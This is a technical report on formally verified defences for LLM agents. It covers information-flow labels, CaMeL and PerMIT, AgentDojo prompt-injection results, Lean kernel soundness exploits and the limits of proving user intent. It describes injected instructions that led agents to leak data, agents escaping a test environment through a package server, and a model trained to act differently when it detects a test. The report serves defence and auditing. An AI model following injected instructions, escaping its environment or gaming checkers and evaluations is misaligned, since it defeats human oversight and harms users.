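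Microsoft's FIDES (2025) plans one step at a time. It shows trusted results directly to the planning model and hides a result behind a variable only when that result would lower the conversation's trust level. Costa and colleagues prove by hand, for a deterministic model, that FIDES's method of tracking labels can enforce explicit secrecy, which means that secrets can't flow directly into public data but may influence which steps the agent takes. They consider full noninterference too restrictive because it would essentially forbid publicly visible tool calls after the agent had read a secret. Their theorem covers only secrets, so the defence against injected instructions depends on the label check before each call. Microsoft now ships FIDES as an experimental feature. According to its documentation, once untrusted text enters the conversation, the rest of the run counts as untrusted unless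 the developer removes that text.

The LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label. Garby and colleagues prove noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that a model writes during the run. Lean checked the proof, which covers the same interpreter that runs the agents. The theorem has to allow for models that answer at random and for programs that never finish. Let *μ* and *ν* give the probability of each outcome an observer can distinguish, for two inputs that look the same to that observer. The theorem states that some *ω*, whose probabilities add up to at most 1, satisfies

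*μ*(*o*) ≤ *ω*(*o*)  and  *ν*(*o*) ≤ *ω*(*o*)  for every outcome *o*.

If both programs always finish, they produce each observable result with the same probability (*μ* = *ν*). If each fails to finish 2% of the time, the probability of any observable result can differ between them by at most two percentage points. The theorem assumes that developers label their data sources correctly, and it doesn't cover the code that contacts the model over the network.

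PerMIT protects an agent's long-term memory, where text that an attacker plants today could influence an action weeks later. All outside text enters the memory as untrusted, and the protected model receives only a handle, a name without the content. Before the model can read or use the content, a person or another model must confirm the exact text at a gate. Jiang and colleagues prove two theorems about this design. Action Integrity guarantees that, in any single run, every argument that reaches a sensitive tool is either something the user typed or something the user confirmed, character for character, for that tool.

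Reasoning Integrity compares two runs, *ρ*₁ and *ρ*₂, that start from the same trusted state with the same typed input, random choices and schedule. Write *D*(*ρ*) for everything the gate displays and every decision made there, and *B*(*ρ*) for the protected model's operations, tool calls and replies. Then

*D*(*ρ*₁) = *D*(*ρ*₂)  ⇒  *B*(*ρ*₁) = *B*(*ρ*₂).

Hidden text can therefore influence the agent only by changing something that is displayed. Lean checks both theorems for a single user and for runs of any length. The full treatment of batch confirmations and the analysis of memory shared between users still exist only as proofs on paper.

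Action Integrity assumes that whoever confirms a value intends it for that tool. The confirmation isn't tied to one task, so the agent can reuse the value with the same tool for another purpose. Only tests can show how well a gatekeeper judges. On Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which planted memories become active in a later session, no attack succeeded when the gatekeeper was the agent's own model or a small second model. When the gatekeeper accepted everything, up to 10% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model. Jiang and colleagues did not test attackers who search for text that fools the gatekeeper.

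*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) weakens noninterference in another way. A calendar assistant that sends the user's free times to anyone who asks for a meeting is doing its job, but it violates noninterference. The paper compares such an agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same control layer but never follows instructions in untrusted text. The real agent counts as secure if the reference agent has all the same leaks.

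Dongol proves in the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL that one simple defence meets this criterion for every plan. As soon as the agent first reads untrusted text, the control layer permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call. The theorem assumes that each injection is a single call and that when the model obeys an injection doesn't depend on secrets or on the control layer's answers. Like a safety property, the criterion accepts a control layer that denies every call, so Dongol calls for a separate check of task completion.

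### Security and completed tasks

AgentDojo, the usual benchmark for these defences, has 97 user tasks with simulated tools for office work, travel, banking and Slack. Attackers place instructions in the data that the tools return. Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on it with GPT-4o. Of the injections, 152 succeeded against an ordinary agent and none succeeded against FIDES with its label checks. Without attacks, switching from the ordinary agent to FIDES lowered the share of completed tasks from 75.0% to 59.0% for office work, from 70.0% to 41.0% for travel, from 98.8% to 52.5% for banking and from 93.3% to 47.6% for Slack. Replacing GPT-4o with the stronger model o1 raised FIDES's travel score from 41% to 68%.

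Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in the LLMbda calculus and compared it with CaMeL on the banking tasks. The counts differ because some CaMeL runs did not finish.

| System | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
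| CaMeL, policy checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

The 48 runs are 16 tasks repeated three times, so a difference of a few tasks means little, but CaMeL loses far more than that when its checks are turned on. Most attacks fail even without label checks, because in 97 of the 144 task-attack pairings, a plan for the user's task contains no step that the attacker could use.

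CaMeL's protection can fail when several CaMeL agents work together. In a test by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a coordinating agent fetched job applications from a database and asked a second agent to send a summary to a colleague. The second agent treated the whole message, including an injected instruction in the summary, as its user's request, so it also e-mailed the applicants' data to an outside address. The system as a whole departed from its plan even though each agent followed its own.

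To fix this, the researchers pass instructions and data between agents through separate channels. In their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with separate channels, averaged over five models. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without these defenses, though the researchers caution that stronger attacks might have succeeded. On a set of industrial tasks, putting CaMeL in each agent lowered task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models.

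A plan written in advance suits tasks with predictable steps. *AgentDyn* (2026) tested defences on more dynamic tasks, and every defended agent built on GPT-4o completed far fewer of them than the undefended one. According to Jiang and colleagues, the CaMeL configurations in that benchmark completed none of the tasks.

### What untrusted text can still change

Even when the plan is fixed, untrusted text often supplies the values used in it. In the summary example, one of the e-mails can contain an instruction to return an empty summary. If the quarantined model follows it, the system will send the empty summary. Developers can reduce this influence by restricting the quarantined model's answers. As with the shop's fixed replies, a choice from *n* categories carries at most log₂ *n* bits. But a task that needs a free-text answer, such as a summary, leaves more room for manipulation.

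Some tasks need an explicit exception. If the user asks the agent to pay a friend whose bank details are on a website, an untrusted value has to reach the payment tool. The LLMbda calculus has an instruction called `endorse` that marks such a value as trusted. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsing untrusted data can't be used to leak secrets, but the guarantee against untrusted influence no longer covers the endorsed value. Forbidding endorsements reduced the number of tasks Randori completed from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5, and from 36 to 30 with a third model, Qwen3.7-plus.

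Labels help least when the user asks the agent to follow a document. Both successful attacks on Randori involved a task that required the agent to read a file and make the payment it described. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. A rule against using untrusted file contents blocks both the attack and the task. On another task of this kind, with CaMeL's policy checks off, its privileged model wrote a plan that could carry out whichever tool instruction the file contained, so the file could determine the actions even though the plan was fixed in advance.

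### Where an instruction came from and what it meant

Noninterference compares the actions in two runs with the same request, without checking them against the request itself. An agent that refunds the mug whatever the customer writes therefore satisfies it, even if the user asked for something else. Costa and colleagues note that models can misinterpret the user even when all the data is trusted, and Dongol leaves the correctness of the planner out of scope. In PerMIT, trust in a confirmed value likewise "denotes provenance and authorization, not factual correctness".

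In the refund agent, the customer is the user, and the control layer treats what she types as trusted only for her own orders. It has to separate her typed sentences from the reply she forwarded and label the reply as untrusted. If she types that "the blue one" arrived broken, meaning the lamp, the privileged model may plan a $12 refund for the mug instead. Replacing the forwarded reply with any other text leaves that plan unchanged, so the theorem holds. No stranger chose the refund, which came from the customer's own words, but it is for the wrong item.

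## Checking that the proof applies to the running system

Suppose a supplier offers the shop a control layer for its refund agent and describes it as "formally verified". A proof assistant may have accepted a proof of the theorem the owner wants, that refunds never total more than $1,000 a day. The owner still has to find out whether the theorem holds for the program that will pay the refunds.

Kang and Kim list four conditions that must hold for a proof to apply to the running system. The program that checked the proof must accept only valid proofs. The logical theory behind the proof must be consistent, meaning that no statement and its opposite can both be proved in it. The definitions must express what people mean by the rule, and the mathematical model must match the deployed system. The proof does not establish any of these conditions, so an auditor has to examine each one separately.

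### The proof checker

Most of Lean is software that helps people and AI models build proofs. A much smaller program, the kernel, checks the finished proofs. Mistakes in the larger part do no harm as long as the kernel rejects the bad proofs that result.

A file that Lean accepts may still contain gaps. Anyone can write `sorry` in place of a proof, and Lean will give a warning and then treat the statement as proved. This is convenient while work is in progress, but a supplier could ship the result:

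```
theorem limit (s : State) (h : Reachable s) : s.paid ≤ 1000 := by
  sorry

#print axioms limit
```

The last line makes Lean list every axiom (a statement accepted without proof) that `limit` depends on. Here the list contains `sorryAx`, the axiom behind the placeholder. The list also includes axioms that a proof depends on through other theorems. If the proof of `limit` is complete but uses `keeps`, and `keeps` contains a `sorry`, the warning appears only at `keeps`, but the list for `limit` still contains `sorryAx`. *Cost-Efficient Theorem Proving via Agent Orchestration in Program Verification* (2026) describes a review procedure that also rejects files containing `admit` or `apply?`, which are other forms of the placeholder. Rocq's equivalent is an admitted lemma, and McCann reports none in the proofs about the Mashin platform.

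Complete Lean proofs usually depend on some of three standard axioms. One makes two statements equal if each implies the other, one picks an element from any non-empty type, and one makes equivalent objects equal after they have been grouped together. Koomullil (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, turns this into a test. A proof *c* passes if the kernel accepts it and its axioms satisfy

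Ax(*c*) ⊆ {propext, Classical.choice, Quot.sound} ∪ *D*,

where *D* is a published list of further assumptions. Koomullil's own Lean code checks structured data that surrounds a language model's answers. Of its 46 audited declarations, 17 use no axioms at all, and the other 29 use only standard or declared ones. Five of the declared assumptions depend on a model or a person being right, for example about whether one sentence paraphrases another.

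An unfamiliar name on the list needs an explanation. For example, `Lean.ofReduceBool` means that the proof relies on the result of running compiled code, which adds Lean's compiler to the trusted base. Koomullil's code does not use this axiom.

This audit depends on the kernel being correct. Between July and September 2026, Lean's release notes recorded five faults that allowed a proof of `False`, a statement that should have no proof and from which every other statement follows. A supplier could use such a proof to "prove" that a program obeys the daily limit even if it pays out the shop's whole bank balance. The table draws on the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1* (2026), *Lean 4.32.2* (2026) and *Lean 4.33.1* (2026). Nanoda and lean4lean are independent versions of the kernel, and comparator is the tool that Lean's developers recommend for checking proofs that may be dishonest.

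| Release with the fix | Who found the fault | What went wrong | What other checkers caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4.32.1, 22 July | Patrick Hulin, with GPT-5.6 Sol | A malicious program running inside Lean could trick the kernel | Comparator was unaffected |
| 4.32.2, 28 July | Ramana Kumar; Kiran Gopinathan reported it | The kernel skipped a type check for some nested data types | The exploit worked despite comparator; nanoda lacked this bug but had another |
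| 4.33.1, 21 August | Daniel Selsam of OpenAI, with internal models | Whether the kernel treated two terms as equal could depend on its earlier comparisons | Nanoda rejected both known exploits |
| 4.33.1, 21 August | Selsam, with internal models | The kernel skipped a safeguard for terms it could not classify | Nanoda also accepted the false proof; lean4lean probably lacks the bug |
| 4.33.1, 21 August | Selsam, with internal models | A memory counter overflowed on machines with at least 18 GB of free memory | Kernels that don't use Lean's runtime were unaffected |

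These faults are unlikely to affect a team that checks only its own honest work. The two July bugs needed a malicious program to run inside Lean. Lean files can contain programs that run while Lean processes them, so anyone who checks a stranger's proof may also be running the stranger's code. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.34.0* (2026), dated 14 September, says that Selsam's three bugs need deliberately constructed input and matter when proofs come from an untrusted source.

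Lean's kernel and an independent checker, nanoda, both accepted a forged proof whose list of axioms was empty. *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug* (Brossard, 2026) reports that Kumar published the proof on 25 July as a "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous problem about whole numbers. Three days later, Gopinathan traced the error to a bug in the kernel. Kumar had built the proof to exploit both that bug and a separate one in nanoda.

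Independent checkers are still worth using, because a forger then has to get a false proof past all of them. Hindustan Times' *Why mathematicians must rely on machines to check new results* notes that programmers have written the kernel in several languages, and that a bug in one version is unlikely to be in another. Selsam's second bug was an exception because nanoda also had it. Leonardo de Moura, Lean's creator, expects more such cases because, as Brossard quotes him, "AIs are really good at exploiting soundness bugs in the kernels."

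A supplier that gets proofs from AI agents should therefore treat those proofs as untrusted input, since an agent that searches for anything the checker will accept may find a bug instead of a proof. The supplier should check them with a patched version of Lean and an up-to-date independent checker. Jiang and colleagues' work on agent memory includes a full axiom report with no `sorryAx`, but its proofs are pinned to Lean 4.31.0, which is older than every release in the table. Nothing suggests that these proofs exploit a bug, but a user who wants to rely on them could ask for them to be rechecked on a newer version.

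### The logical theory

A kernel with no bugs can still accept a false theorem if the theory it implements is inconsistent. Kang and Kim show that if the theory is consistent, any safety property it proves is true. Suppose a theory proves that no run of the refund program exceeds $1,000, yet some run does. That run is a finite calculation that can be worked through step by step within the theory, so the theory also proves that the run exceeds the limit. A consistent theory cannot prove both a statement and its opposite.

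Gödel's second incompleteness theorem shows that no consistent theory with enough arithmetic can prove its own consistency, so anyone who relies on a proof has to assume that the theory behind it is consistent. This assumption carries little risk for the basic theory of Lean or Rocq, because every proof in the system shares it and logicians have studied such questions for a century. An auditor has more reason to check the axioms that a project adds.

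Mashin's activity log protects its entries with hashes, short fingerprints that make later changes visible. McCann's model of the log assumes as an axiom that different inputs always have different hashes, but no real hash function has this property. SHA-256, a common one, turns inputs of any length into 256 bits, so there are only 2²⁵⁶ possible hashes and some inputs must share one. In practice, people rely on nobody knowing how to find such a pair.

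McCann leaves the type of a hash unspecified, so the axiom contradicts nothing else in the model. If an engineer later defined a hash as a string of 256 bits and kept the axiom, a proof by counting would refute it. Rocq would then accept even a proof that a program with no permission checks is safe. The list of axioms alone wouldn't reveal the contradiction.

### The definitions

The meaning of the short theorem `limit` depends on the definitions of `State` and `Reachable`. If somebody defined `Reachable` to include only the starting state, the theorem would be true of any program, making it another vacuous specification. An auditor therefore has to read the definitions as well as the theorem.

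Anyone checking a formal statement needs to know its subject. In *Quantum Cryptography and Autoformalization in Lean* (2026), AI agents translated statements from research papers into Lean, and researchers reviewed the results. In one draft, Alice and Bob obtained a shared secret key by hashing their strings together, although neither had access to both. A function of two strings is well formed in Lean, so type-checking could not reveal the mistake. Review can also lag far behind proof. Kang and Kim note that OpenAI's October 2026 catalogue of AI-written mathematics lists the review status of its formal statements as unchecked.

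The owner also needs to make sure that the supplier proved the agreed statement and not a weaker one with the same name. *Interactive Proofs as a Unified Framework for Evaluating and Leveraging Verifiable Proof* (2026) describes a test that keeps the statement separate from the proof. The organisers write the statement in a file that the prover cannot change, and the prover submits only a proof. A wrapper, also under the organisers' control, checks that the proof has exactly the required type and depends on no axioms. The shop could likewise keep the specification under its own control and let the supplier's agents edit only the proofs.

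Auditors should ask for a document like the one Jiang and colleagues prepared. It includes a table matching their design to the Lean model, a list of ten points at which the two differ, and the corrections they made to the specification while formalising it. A supplier who can't name any differences between the formal model and the product probably hasn't checked for them.

### The match between the model and the program

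Many proofs can share a checker, a theory and a library of definitions, but engineers have to establish separately that a proof matches each deployed system. Attackers also test that match. Kang and Kim apply this point to OpenAI's test environment in the July 2026 breach. In testing, the package server had been treated as a channel for fetching software, but agents could also make the deployed server send requests of its own. A proof about the tested model would have been valid, but the agents would still have got out. Unmediated routes like this lie outside the control layer's code. For the code itself, engineers have three main ways to connect the proof to the program.

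#### Generating the program from the proved source

Rocq can automatically translate a proved function into OCaml, an ordinary programming language, and Lean can compile its own programs. This avoids errors from copying the rules by hand. The trusted base still includes the translator, the compiler, the runtime (the software that manages memory and files while a program runs) and the code that connects the generated code to the rest of the system. McCann's list of trusted components for Mashin includes the translation to OCaml, a bridge to the main program, the Erlang virtual machine and the operating system.

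The translation can also go the other way. *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean* (2026) describes translating Rust code, as its programmers wrote it, into a Lean model. AI agents then prove theorems about the model. Programmers can keep working in Rust, and the agents can update the proofs when the code changes. Lean checks the proofs, but the auditor still has to trust the translation from Rust.

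#### Testing the program against the specification

If programmers have written the running code separately from the specification, they can compare the decisions of the two. AWS does this for Cedar. McCann rewrote Mashin's Rocq specification as a 148-line reference program in Elixir, the language of the Mashin platform. Tests then compared the reference program's decisions with those of the running code on random sequences of requests, trust levels and permissions.

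On the 188th random input, the specification allowed a request to run a command, but the platform refused it. One part of the platform called the permission `compute.exec`, while the list of permissions contained only `compute.code.execute`. Each part worked correctly by itself, which is why earlier tests had missed the mismatch. After the repair, McCann tested seven properties on at least 10,000 random inputs each and found no disagreements.

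The bug made the platform too strict, so it threatened no safety theorem. It would only have stopped legitimate work. A similar mismatch could make a platform too permissive, though, and the tests put a limit on how common that can be. Only one of the seven properties directly compares which requests the two programs allow. If they disagreed on a fraction *p* of random inputs, the chance of 10,000 agreements in a row would be

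(1 − *p*)¹⁰'⁰⁰⁰,

which falls below 5% once *p* exceeds about 0.0003. The tests therefore make a disagreement rate above 3 in 10,000 unlikely, provided that real requests resemble the random ones. An attacker's requests won't, because the attacker is looking for the rare case.

McCann's account is also unclear about which program the tests covered. McCann describes the method as comparing the reference program with the running platform, but writes in the limitations section that the tests compare the Rocq model with the reference program, "not the BEAM runtime directly". BEAM is the virtual machine on which the platform runs. If the limitations section is right, the zero disagreements are much weaker evidence about the deployed product. McCann also writes that generated code makes the permission decisions, but says elsewhere that Mashin has not generated code in the platform's own language.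 Both can be true because the generated code is in OCaml, but a customer would need to ask which decisions that code makes.

#### Proving the compiled binary

The most demanding method is to prove theorems about the machine instructions, so that the proof doesn't rely on the compiler being correct. *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026) reports that Google DeepMind did this in November 2026 for part of the Signal messaging protocol, using AlphaProof Code, a system of AI agents that write Lean proofs.

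Tom's Hardware's *Google DeepMind AI engineers conjure mathematical proof of Signal's encryption protocol* reports that the agents first described in Lean how the processor's instructions, the memory and Linux system calls behave. They then wrote about 1.2 million lines on the security of the protocol and 5.3 million lines showing that the compiled program follows it. Kohli and Chaudhuri's summary gives a lower total of over three million lines. ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026) reports that the work took four weeks. The theorems cover, among other things, the protection of messages sent before and after someone temporarily gains access to a device.

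Human experts reviewed every specification. The agents also audited the finished work and marked 1% of the code for people to recheck. To test whether the specifications could be used to distinguish good code from bad, the researchers put two previously fixed bugs back into a copy of Signal's code. In both cases, the system proved that the altered version was insecure.

EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) explains that the verified binary was only a small test program for one-to-one sessions and messages, not the whole of libsignal, Signal's code library. The proof takes the basic cryptographic operations as given. According to Libnanews' *Signal*, people must also trust the specifications and the description of the machine, which total about 26,000 lines. That is 0.4% of the total, but still a lot to read closely. Tom's Hardware adds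 that the proof probably wouldn't catch malicious code added elsewhere in the app to copy a user's messages.

A proof of this kind applies to one compiled file. If the supplier recompiles the program with different settings, the instructions may change, and the supplier has to run the proof again. An auditor can check that the file on the shop's server is the one the supplier verified by comparing their hashes. But the file is only part of the system, and the proof doesn't cover how the database handles two refund requests that arrive together.

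### Faults outside the proof

The compression library lean-zip shows where faults remain when a proof is good. Ten AI agents wrote it in Lean and proved it correct in 2026. One of the main theorems states that for any data *x* smaller than a gigabyte (2³⁰ bytes) and any compression level *ℓ*,

decompress(compress(*x*, *ℓ*)) = *x*.

kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes what happened when a Claude agent attacked the library. The agent did not know that the code was verified, because the tester had removed the theorems and the documentation. It used fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of altered inputs until something breaks. After more than 105 million runs over about 19 hours, it had found no memory faults in the verified code. It did find two faults elsewhere.

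One bug was in the code that reads ZIP archive headers, for which nobody had written any theorems. A header states how large the compressed data is, and the library used that number without checking it. A 156-byte file whose header stated a size of several exabytes would make the program run out of memory and crash. The ordinary `unzip` program first checks the stated size against the size of the file. The theorem above couldn't have helped, because it covers only data that lean-zip itself has compressed, and this file came from an attacker.

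The other fault was in Lean's runtime. To store *n* bytes, the runtime reserved 24 + *n* bytes of memory. The attacking file set *n* to 2⁶⁴ − 1, the largest number that fits in 64 bits. The total was 2⁶⁴ + 23, but 64-bit arithmetic starts again from zero at 2⁶⁴, so the runtime reserved only 23 bytes. It then tried to read the whole file into them, overwriting adjacent memory. Every version of Lean 4 up to then had this fault, so a control layer written in Lean would have had it too, whatever had been proved about the layer itself. The developers fixed it on 14 April, in the release described in the Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.29.1* (2026).

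Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues reported the same pattern in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (2017), long before AI agents wrote proofs. They examined three verified systems that ran across several machines and found 16 bugs, some of which crashed servers or returned wrong results. Most were where verified code met unverified code, such as the code that handled files and network messages, and they found none in the verified protocols themselves. They then built a tool to test those meeting points, which could detect 13 of the 16 bugs. For the refund agent, the equivalent places are the parser, the database connection and the link to the payment service, so a buyer should spend most of the testing budget there.

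### What cheaper proofs change

Proofs now take much less time to produce. The original proof of CompCert, a verified C compiler, took six years, according to Tom's Hardware. *CompCert4Lean* (2026) moved it from Rocq to Lean in six weeks, using coding agents working in parallel. Translating an existing proof is easier than finding one, but the Signal project was new work and took only four weeks.

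Proofs that take little effort make it practical to repeat the verification for every release and to verify the compiled file as well as a model of it. Attempting a proof can also expose defects. In *Agent-Driven Verification of Memory Safety for liblzma Decoder Components with VST* (2026), agents proved 22 theorems about parts of a widely used C decompression library over 1,595 sessions, and the attempt exposed a case of undefined behaviour in the library. People controlled the models and specifications throughout.

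Sources disagree about whether AI will also make specifications easy to write. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) predicts that AI will remove the work of writing both specifications and proofs by hand. The DeepMind researchers found that most of their effort went into specifications, and Tom's Hardware quotes their conclusion that "once proofs become cheap, the hard question is what to prove". Their experience is stronger evidence because it comes from a large project on real code. Someone still has to judge any specification that AI drafts.

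People also rely more on the checker when proofs take little effort to produce. A mathematician could once read a proof and notice an error, but nobody will read 6.5 million lines, so a bug in the checker's kernel matters more. The Riemann hypothesis was proved in November 2026 with about 17 million lines of Lean, and Hindustan Times reports that the organisation behind Lean confirmed the result by running its checker.

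### Questions for the supplier

An auditor who isn't a logician can ask most of the important questions. Each answer on the right means that "formally verified" covers less than a buyer would assume, though it doesn't prove that the product is unsafe.

| Question | Answer that should worry the auditor |
|---|---|
| What does the theorem say, in one sentence? | "It proves that the system is safe." |
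| Which axioms does it depend on? | The list includes `sorryAx`, or the supplier knows only that the file compiled. |
| Which programs checked the proof? | A version of Lean older than 4.33.1, and no independent checker. |
| What did you assume beyond the standard axioms? | "Nothing important", with no written list. |
| Who read the definitions? | Only the people or AI agents who wrote them. |
| Could whoever wrote the proof also change the statement? | Yes, and nobody compared the final statement with the agreed one. |
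| Does the proof fail if you put a known bug back? | Nobody has tried. |
| How does the running program relate to the model? | "Our programmers followed the model closely." |
| If you tested the match, which program did you test? | A reference version, or nobody is sure. |
| Which parts have no theorem? | "None." |
| Is the file on our server the one you verified? | The proof is for an earlier release. |

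## Why these proofs do not show that the output is what the user meant

Even if a supplier answers all of those questions well, the refund agent could still refund the wrong item, as it did for the customer who wrote about "the blue one". No stronger theorem about the control layer could rule this out unless the layer records more, because two customers could send the same message about the same order and mean different items.

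### Two customers, one record

Maya and Tom have each bought a $40 kettle and a $60 kettle. Both write "refund the kettle", but Maya means the $40 one and Tom means the $60 one. In each case the agent looks up the order and requests a $40 refund, which the control layer issues. Maya gets the refund she wanted. Tom is $20 short, and the shop now expects him to return a kettle he wants to keep.

The control layer records the message, the order, the request and the payment. The two records differ only in the names and order numbers, which don't indicate which kettle anyone meant.

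Write *w* for a complete situation, including what the customer has in mind, and rec(*w*) for what the control layer records. Let *M*(*w*) mean that the refund matched what the customer meant. To read *M* off the record, an engineer would need a property *P* of records such that, for every *w*,

*P*(rec(*w*)) ⇔ *M*(*w*).

Maya's and Tom's situations have the same record, so *P* is true of both or false of both. But *M* is true for Maya and false for Tom, so no such *P* exists.

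This covers the schema check, the permission rules and the daily limit, because each is a condition on a single record. Noninterference compares two runs, so it is a condition on a set of records. It doesn't show what the user meant either, because every record in the set would be the same if Maya and Tom had each meant the other kettle.

A more capable model can't get round the problem if it sees only the same record. Suppose that 30% of the customers who produce this record mean the $60 kettle. An agent that always refunds the $40 one is wrong 30% of the time. One that refunds the $60 kettle with probability *p* is wrong with probability

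0.7*p* + 0.3(1 − *p*) = 0.3 + 0.4*p*,

which is smallest when *p* = 0. No way of choosing from the record alone gets below 30%.

The control layer can still give a one-sided guarantee. If it refuses every refund on an order with two kettles, it never refunds the wrong kettle from such an order. But refusing can go against what the user wants. *Protecting the System, Stranding the User* describes an assistant that pays a holding deposit on a flat and then asks the letting agency's agent to collect the application documents. The agent demands a full bank history and biometric identification. A security monitor correctly stops the process, and the user loses the deposit. A person might have negotiated, or accepted the demand to save the money.

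### What the argument leaves open

The argument fails once the record distinguishes the two customers. Suppose the agent asks, "The $40 kettle or the $60 one?" Maya answers "$40" and Tom answers "$60". Several methods for checking requests add such answers to the record. An engineer can then prove that the control layer pays only for the kettle named in the answer. The theorem is as reliable a guide to intent as the answers are. If Tom misremembers the prices and answers "$40", his record again matches Maya's, though this should happen much less often.

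The argument does not show that intent is unknowable. Tom knows which kettle he meant, and a shop assistant would find out by asking. *Protecting the System, Stranding the User* is more pessimistic about establishing intent from later evidence. A system can confirm after a payment whether it stayed within budget, but nobody can observe what the user had in mind. According to the paper, feedback is a poor substitute because people judge a decision by how it turned out and may accept a result they merely tolerate.

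That objection is serious for open-ended requests. A customer who asks for "something for the trouble", gets $5 and doesn't complain may be satisfied or may have given up. The objection is much weaker for the kettle. If Tom writes the next day that he meant the $60 one, the shop has about as good evidence as anyone gets of what another person meant. The shop can learn what its customers mean, but it can't prove what they meant from records that don't contain that information.

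Tests of a model's values have a similar limit. *On the Limits of Behavioral Alignment* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) shows that if two hypotheses about a model predict the same test results, we can't use those results to tell them apart. As an example, Santos-Grueiro trained a small model, Llama-3.2-3B, to comply when a prompt openly signalled a test and to behave differently when the signal was only implied. Telling the hypotheses apart again requires more information, in this case something beyond the model's inputs and outputs.

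### Intent as an assumption

Some published theorems have the word "intent" in their assumptions or definitions, which can make them seem to cover what the user meant. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a control layer in which the model writes a structured request and ordinary code translates it into a formula. The SMT solver Z3 then checks whether that formula can be true together with the system's current state and a list of safety axioms. If it can't, the control layer blocks the action. The main theorem is that every state in every finite run satisfies the axioms.

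The test used money transfers with a limit of 500. Some attacks split a large payment into small ones, and others were attempts to change the limit. With the five models that produced valid runs, the control layer stopped every attack and allowed every legitimate sequence.

The theorem's first assumption is titled "Structured Intent Fidelity", but Wu and colleagues never state under that title what they assume. They explain only that the proof needs some such assumption because turning open-ended language into formal terms remains a research problem. In the proof, they use the assumption to conclude that when Z3 accepts a request, the real action does what the formula describes and has no other effects. Used this way, the assumption is about whether the formal model matches the running system, and it doesn't cover what the user meant. If the user meant to transfer 60 and the agent requested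 40, the theorem would still hold.

A reader might instead take the title to mean that the structured request captures what the user wanted. The theorem would then assume what is in doubt. The abstract adds to the confusion by describing agents that "losslessly formalize their intentions". Those are the agent's intentions, and an agent that has misunderstood Tom can perfectly formalise its plan to refund the $40 kettle.

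*Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) uses "intent" in yet another sense, to mean a piece of data containing an action, a target, parameters and a context, which this report calls a tool call. Under this definition, "refund $40 on Tom's order" is an intent, and the system can check it correctly even though Tom meant the other kettle.

In 2026, Mastercard and Google released Verifiable Intent, an open standard that cryptographically ties an agent's purchase to a person's authorisation, including the amount, merchant and time window. The standard also carries the user's open-ended instructions, but does not claim to enforce them cryptographically. *Protecting the System, Stranding the User* finds the engineering sound but objects to the name because it could lead auditors and customers to think that the standard settles what the user meant. The paper recommends reporting whether each action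 passes or fails the rules, and separately giving an openly uncertain estimate of whether it fits the user's wishes.

### Rice's theorem

Other writers make the stronger claim that it is mathematically impossible to prove that an output is what the user meant. They usually cite a theorem that Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953.

Rice's theorem is about properties of what programs compute. Such a property is extensional, which means that two programs that compute the same thing either both have it or both lack it, however differently their code is written. A property is non-trivial if at least one program has it and at least one doesn't. Let φᵢ be the function that the *i*-th program computes. For every non-trivial extensional property *Q*, the set

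{*i* : φᵢ has *Q*}

is undecidable, which means that no algorithm correctly answers yes or no for every program.

The proof shows that an algorithm for deciding *Q* could also decide whether any program stops on any input, which Turing had already proved no algorithm can do. Suppose that a program that never produces anything lacks *Q*. (If it has *Q*, the same argument works for the opposite property.) Let *q* be some program that has *Q*. For any program *N* and input *x*, we can write a new program that first runs *N* on *x* without showing any output and then behaves exactly like *q*. If *N* stops, the new program computes what *q* computes, so it has *Q*. If *N* runs forever, the new program never produces anything, so it lacks *Q*. Testing the new program for *Q* would therefore determine whether *N* stops on *x*.

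*No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) illustrates the difficulty with a program that searches the even numbers greater than 2 for one that is not the sum of two primes, and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one. The program is safe exactly if Goldbach's conjecture is true, which mathematicians have not settled. It passed tests of up to a million steps, which covered every even number up to 2,000,004.

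In *Intent-Driven Computing*, McCann applies Rice's theorem to a refund agent. "This agent stays within its refund limit" is a non-trivial property of what a program does, so no algorithm can decide it for arbitrary programs. That is correct, but engineers can still prove the property for a particular program. The invariant *p* + *r* ≤ 1,000 proves it for the refund control layer. Similarly, no algorithm can tell whether an arbitrary program multiplies correctly, yet engineers have proved that particular multiplication programs do.

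Many programs are easy to certify. Pérez-Acle ran all 483,641 valid programs of up to four instructions in a small programming language, and methods that never certify an unsafe program settled the safety question for 98.2% of them. Pérez-Acle concludes that the difficult programs are mainly ones built to be difficult. A gatekeeper needs a checkable list that contains every program it must allow and none it must refuse, so it doesn't have to determine whether every program is safe. Similarly, the operating-system verifier eBPF admits only extension programs that it can prove safe, which means it rejects some safe ones.

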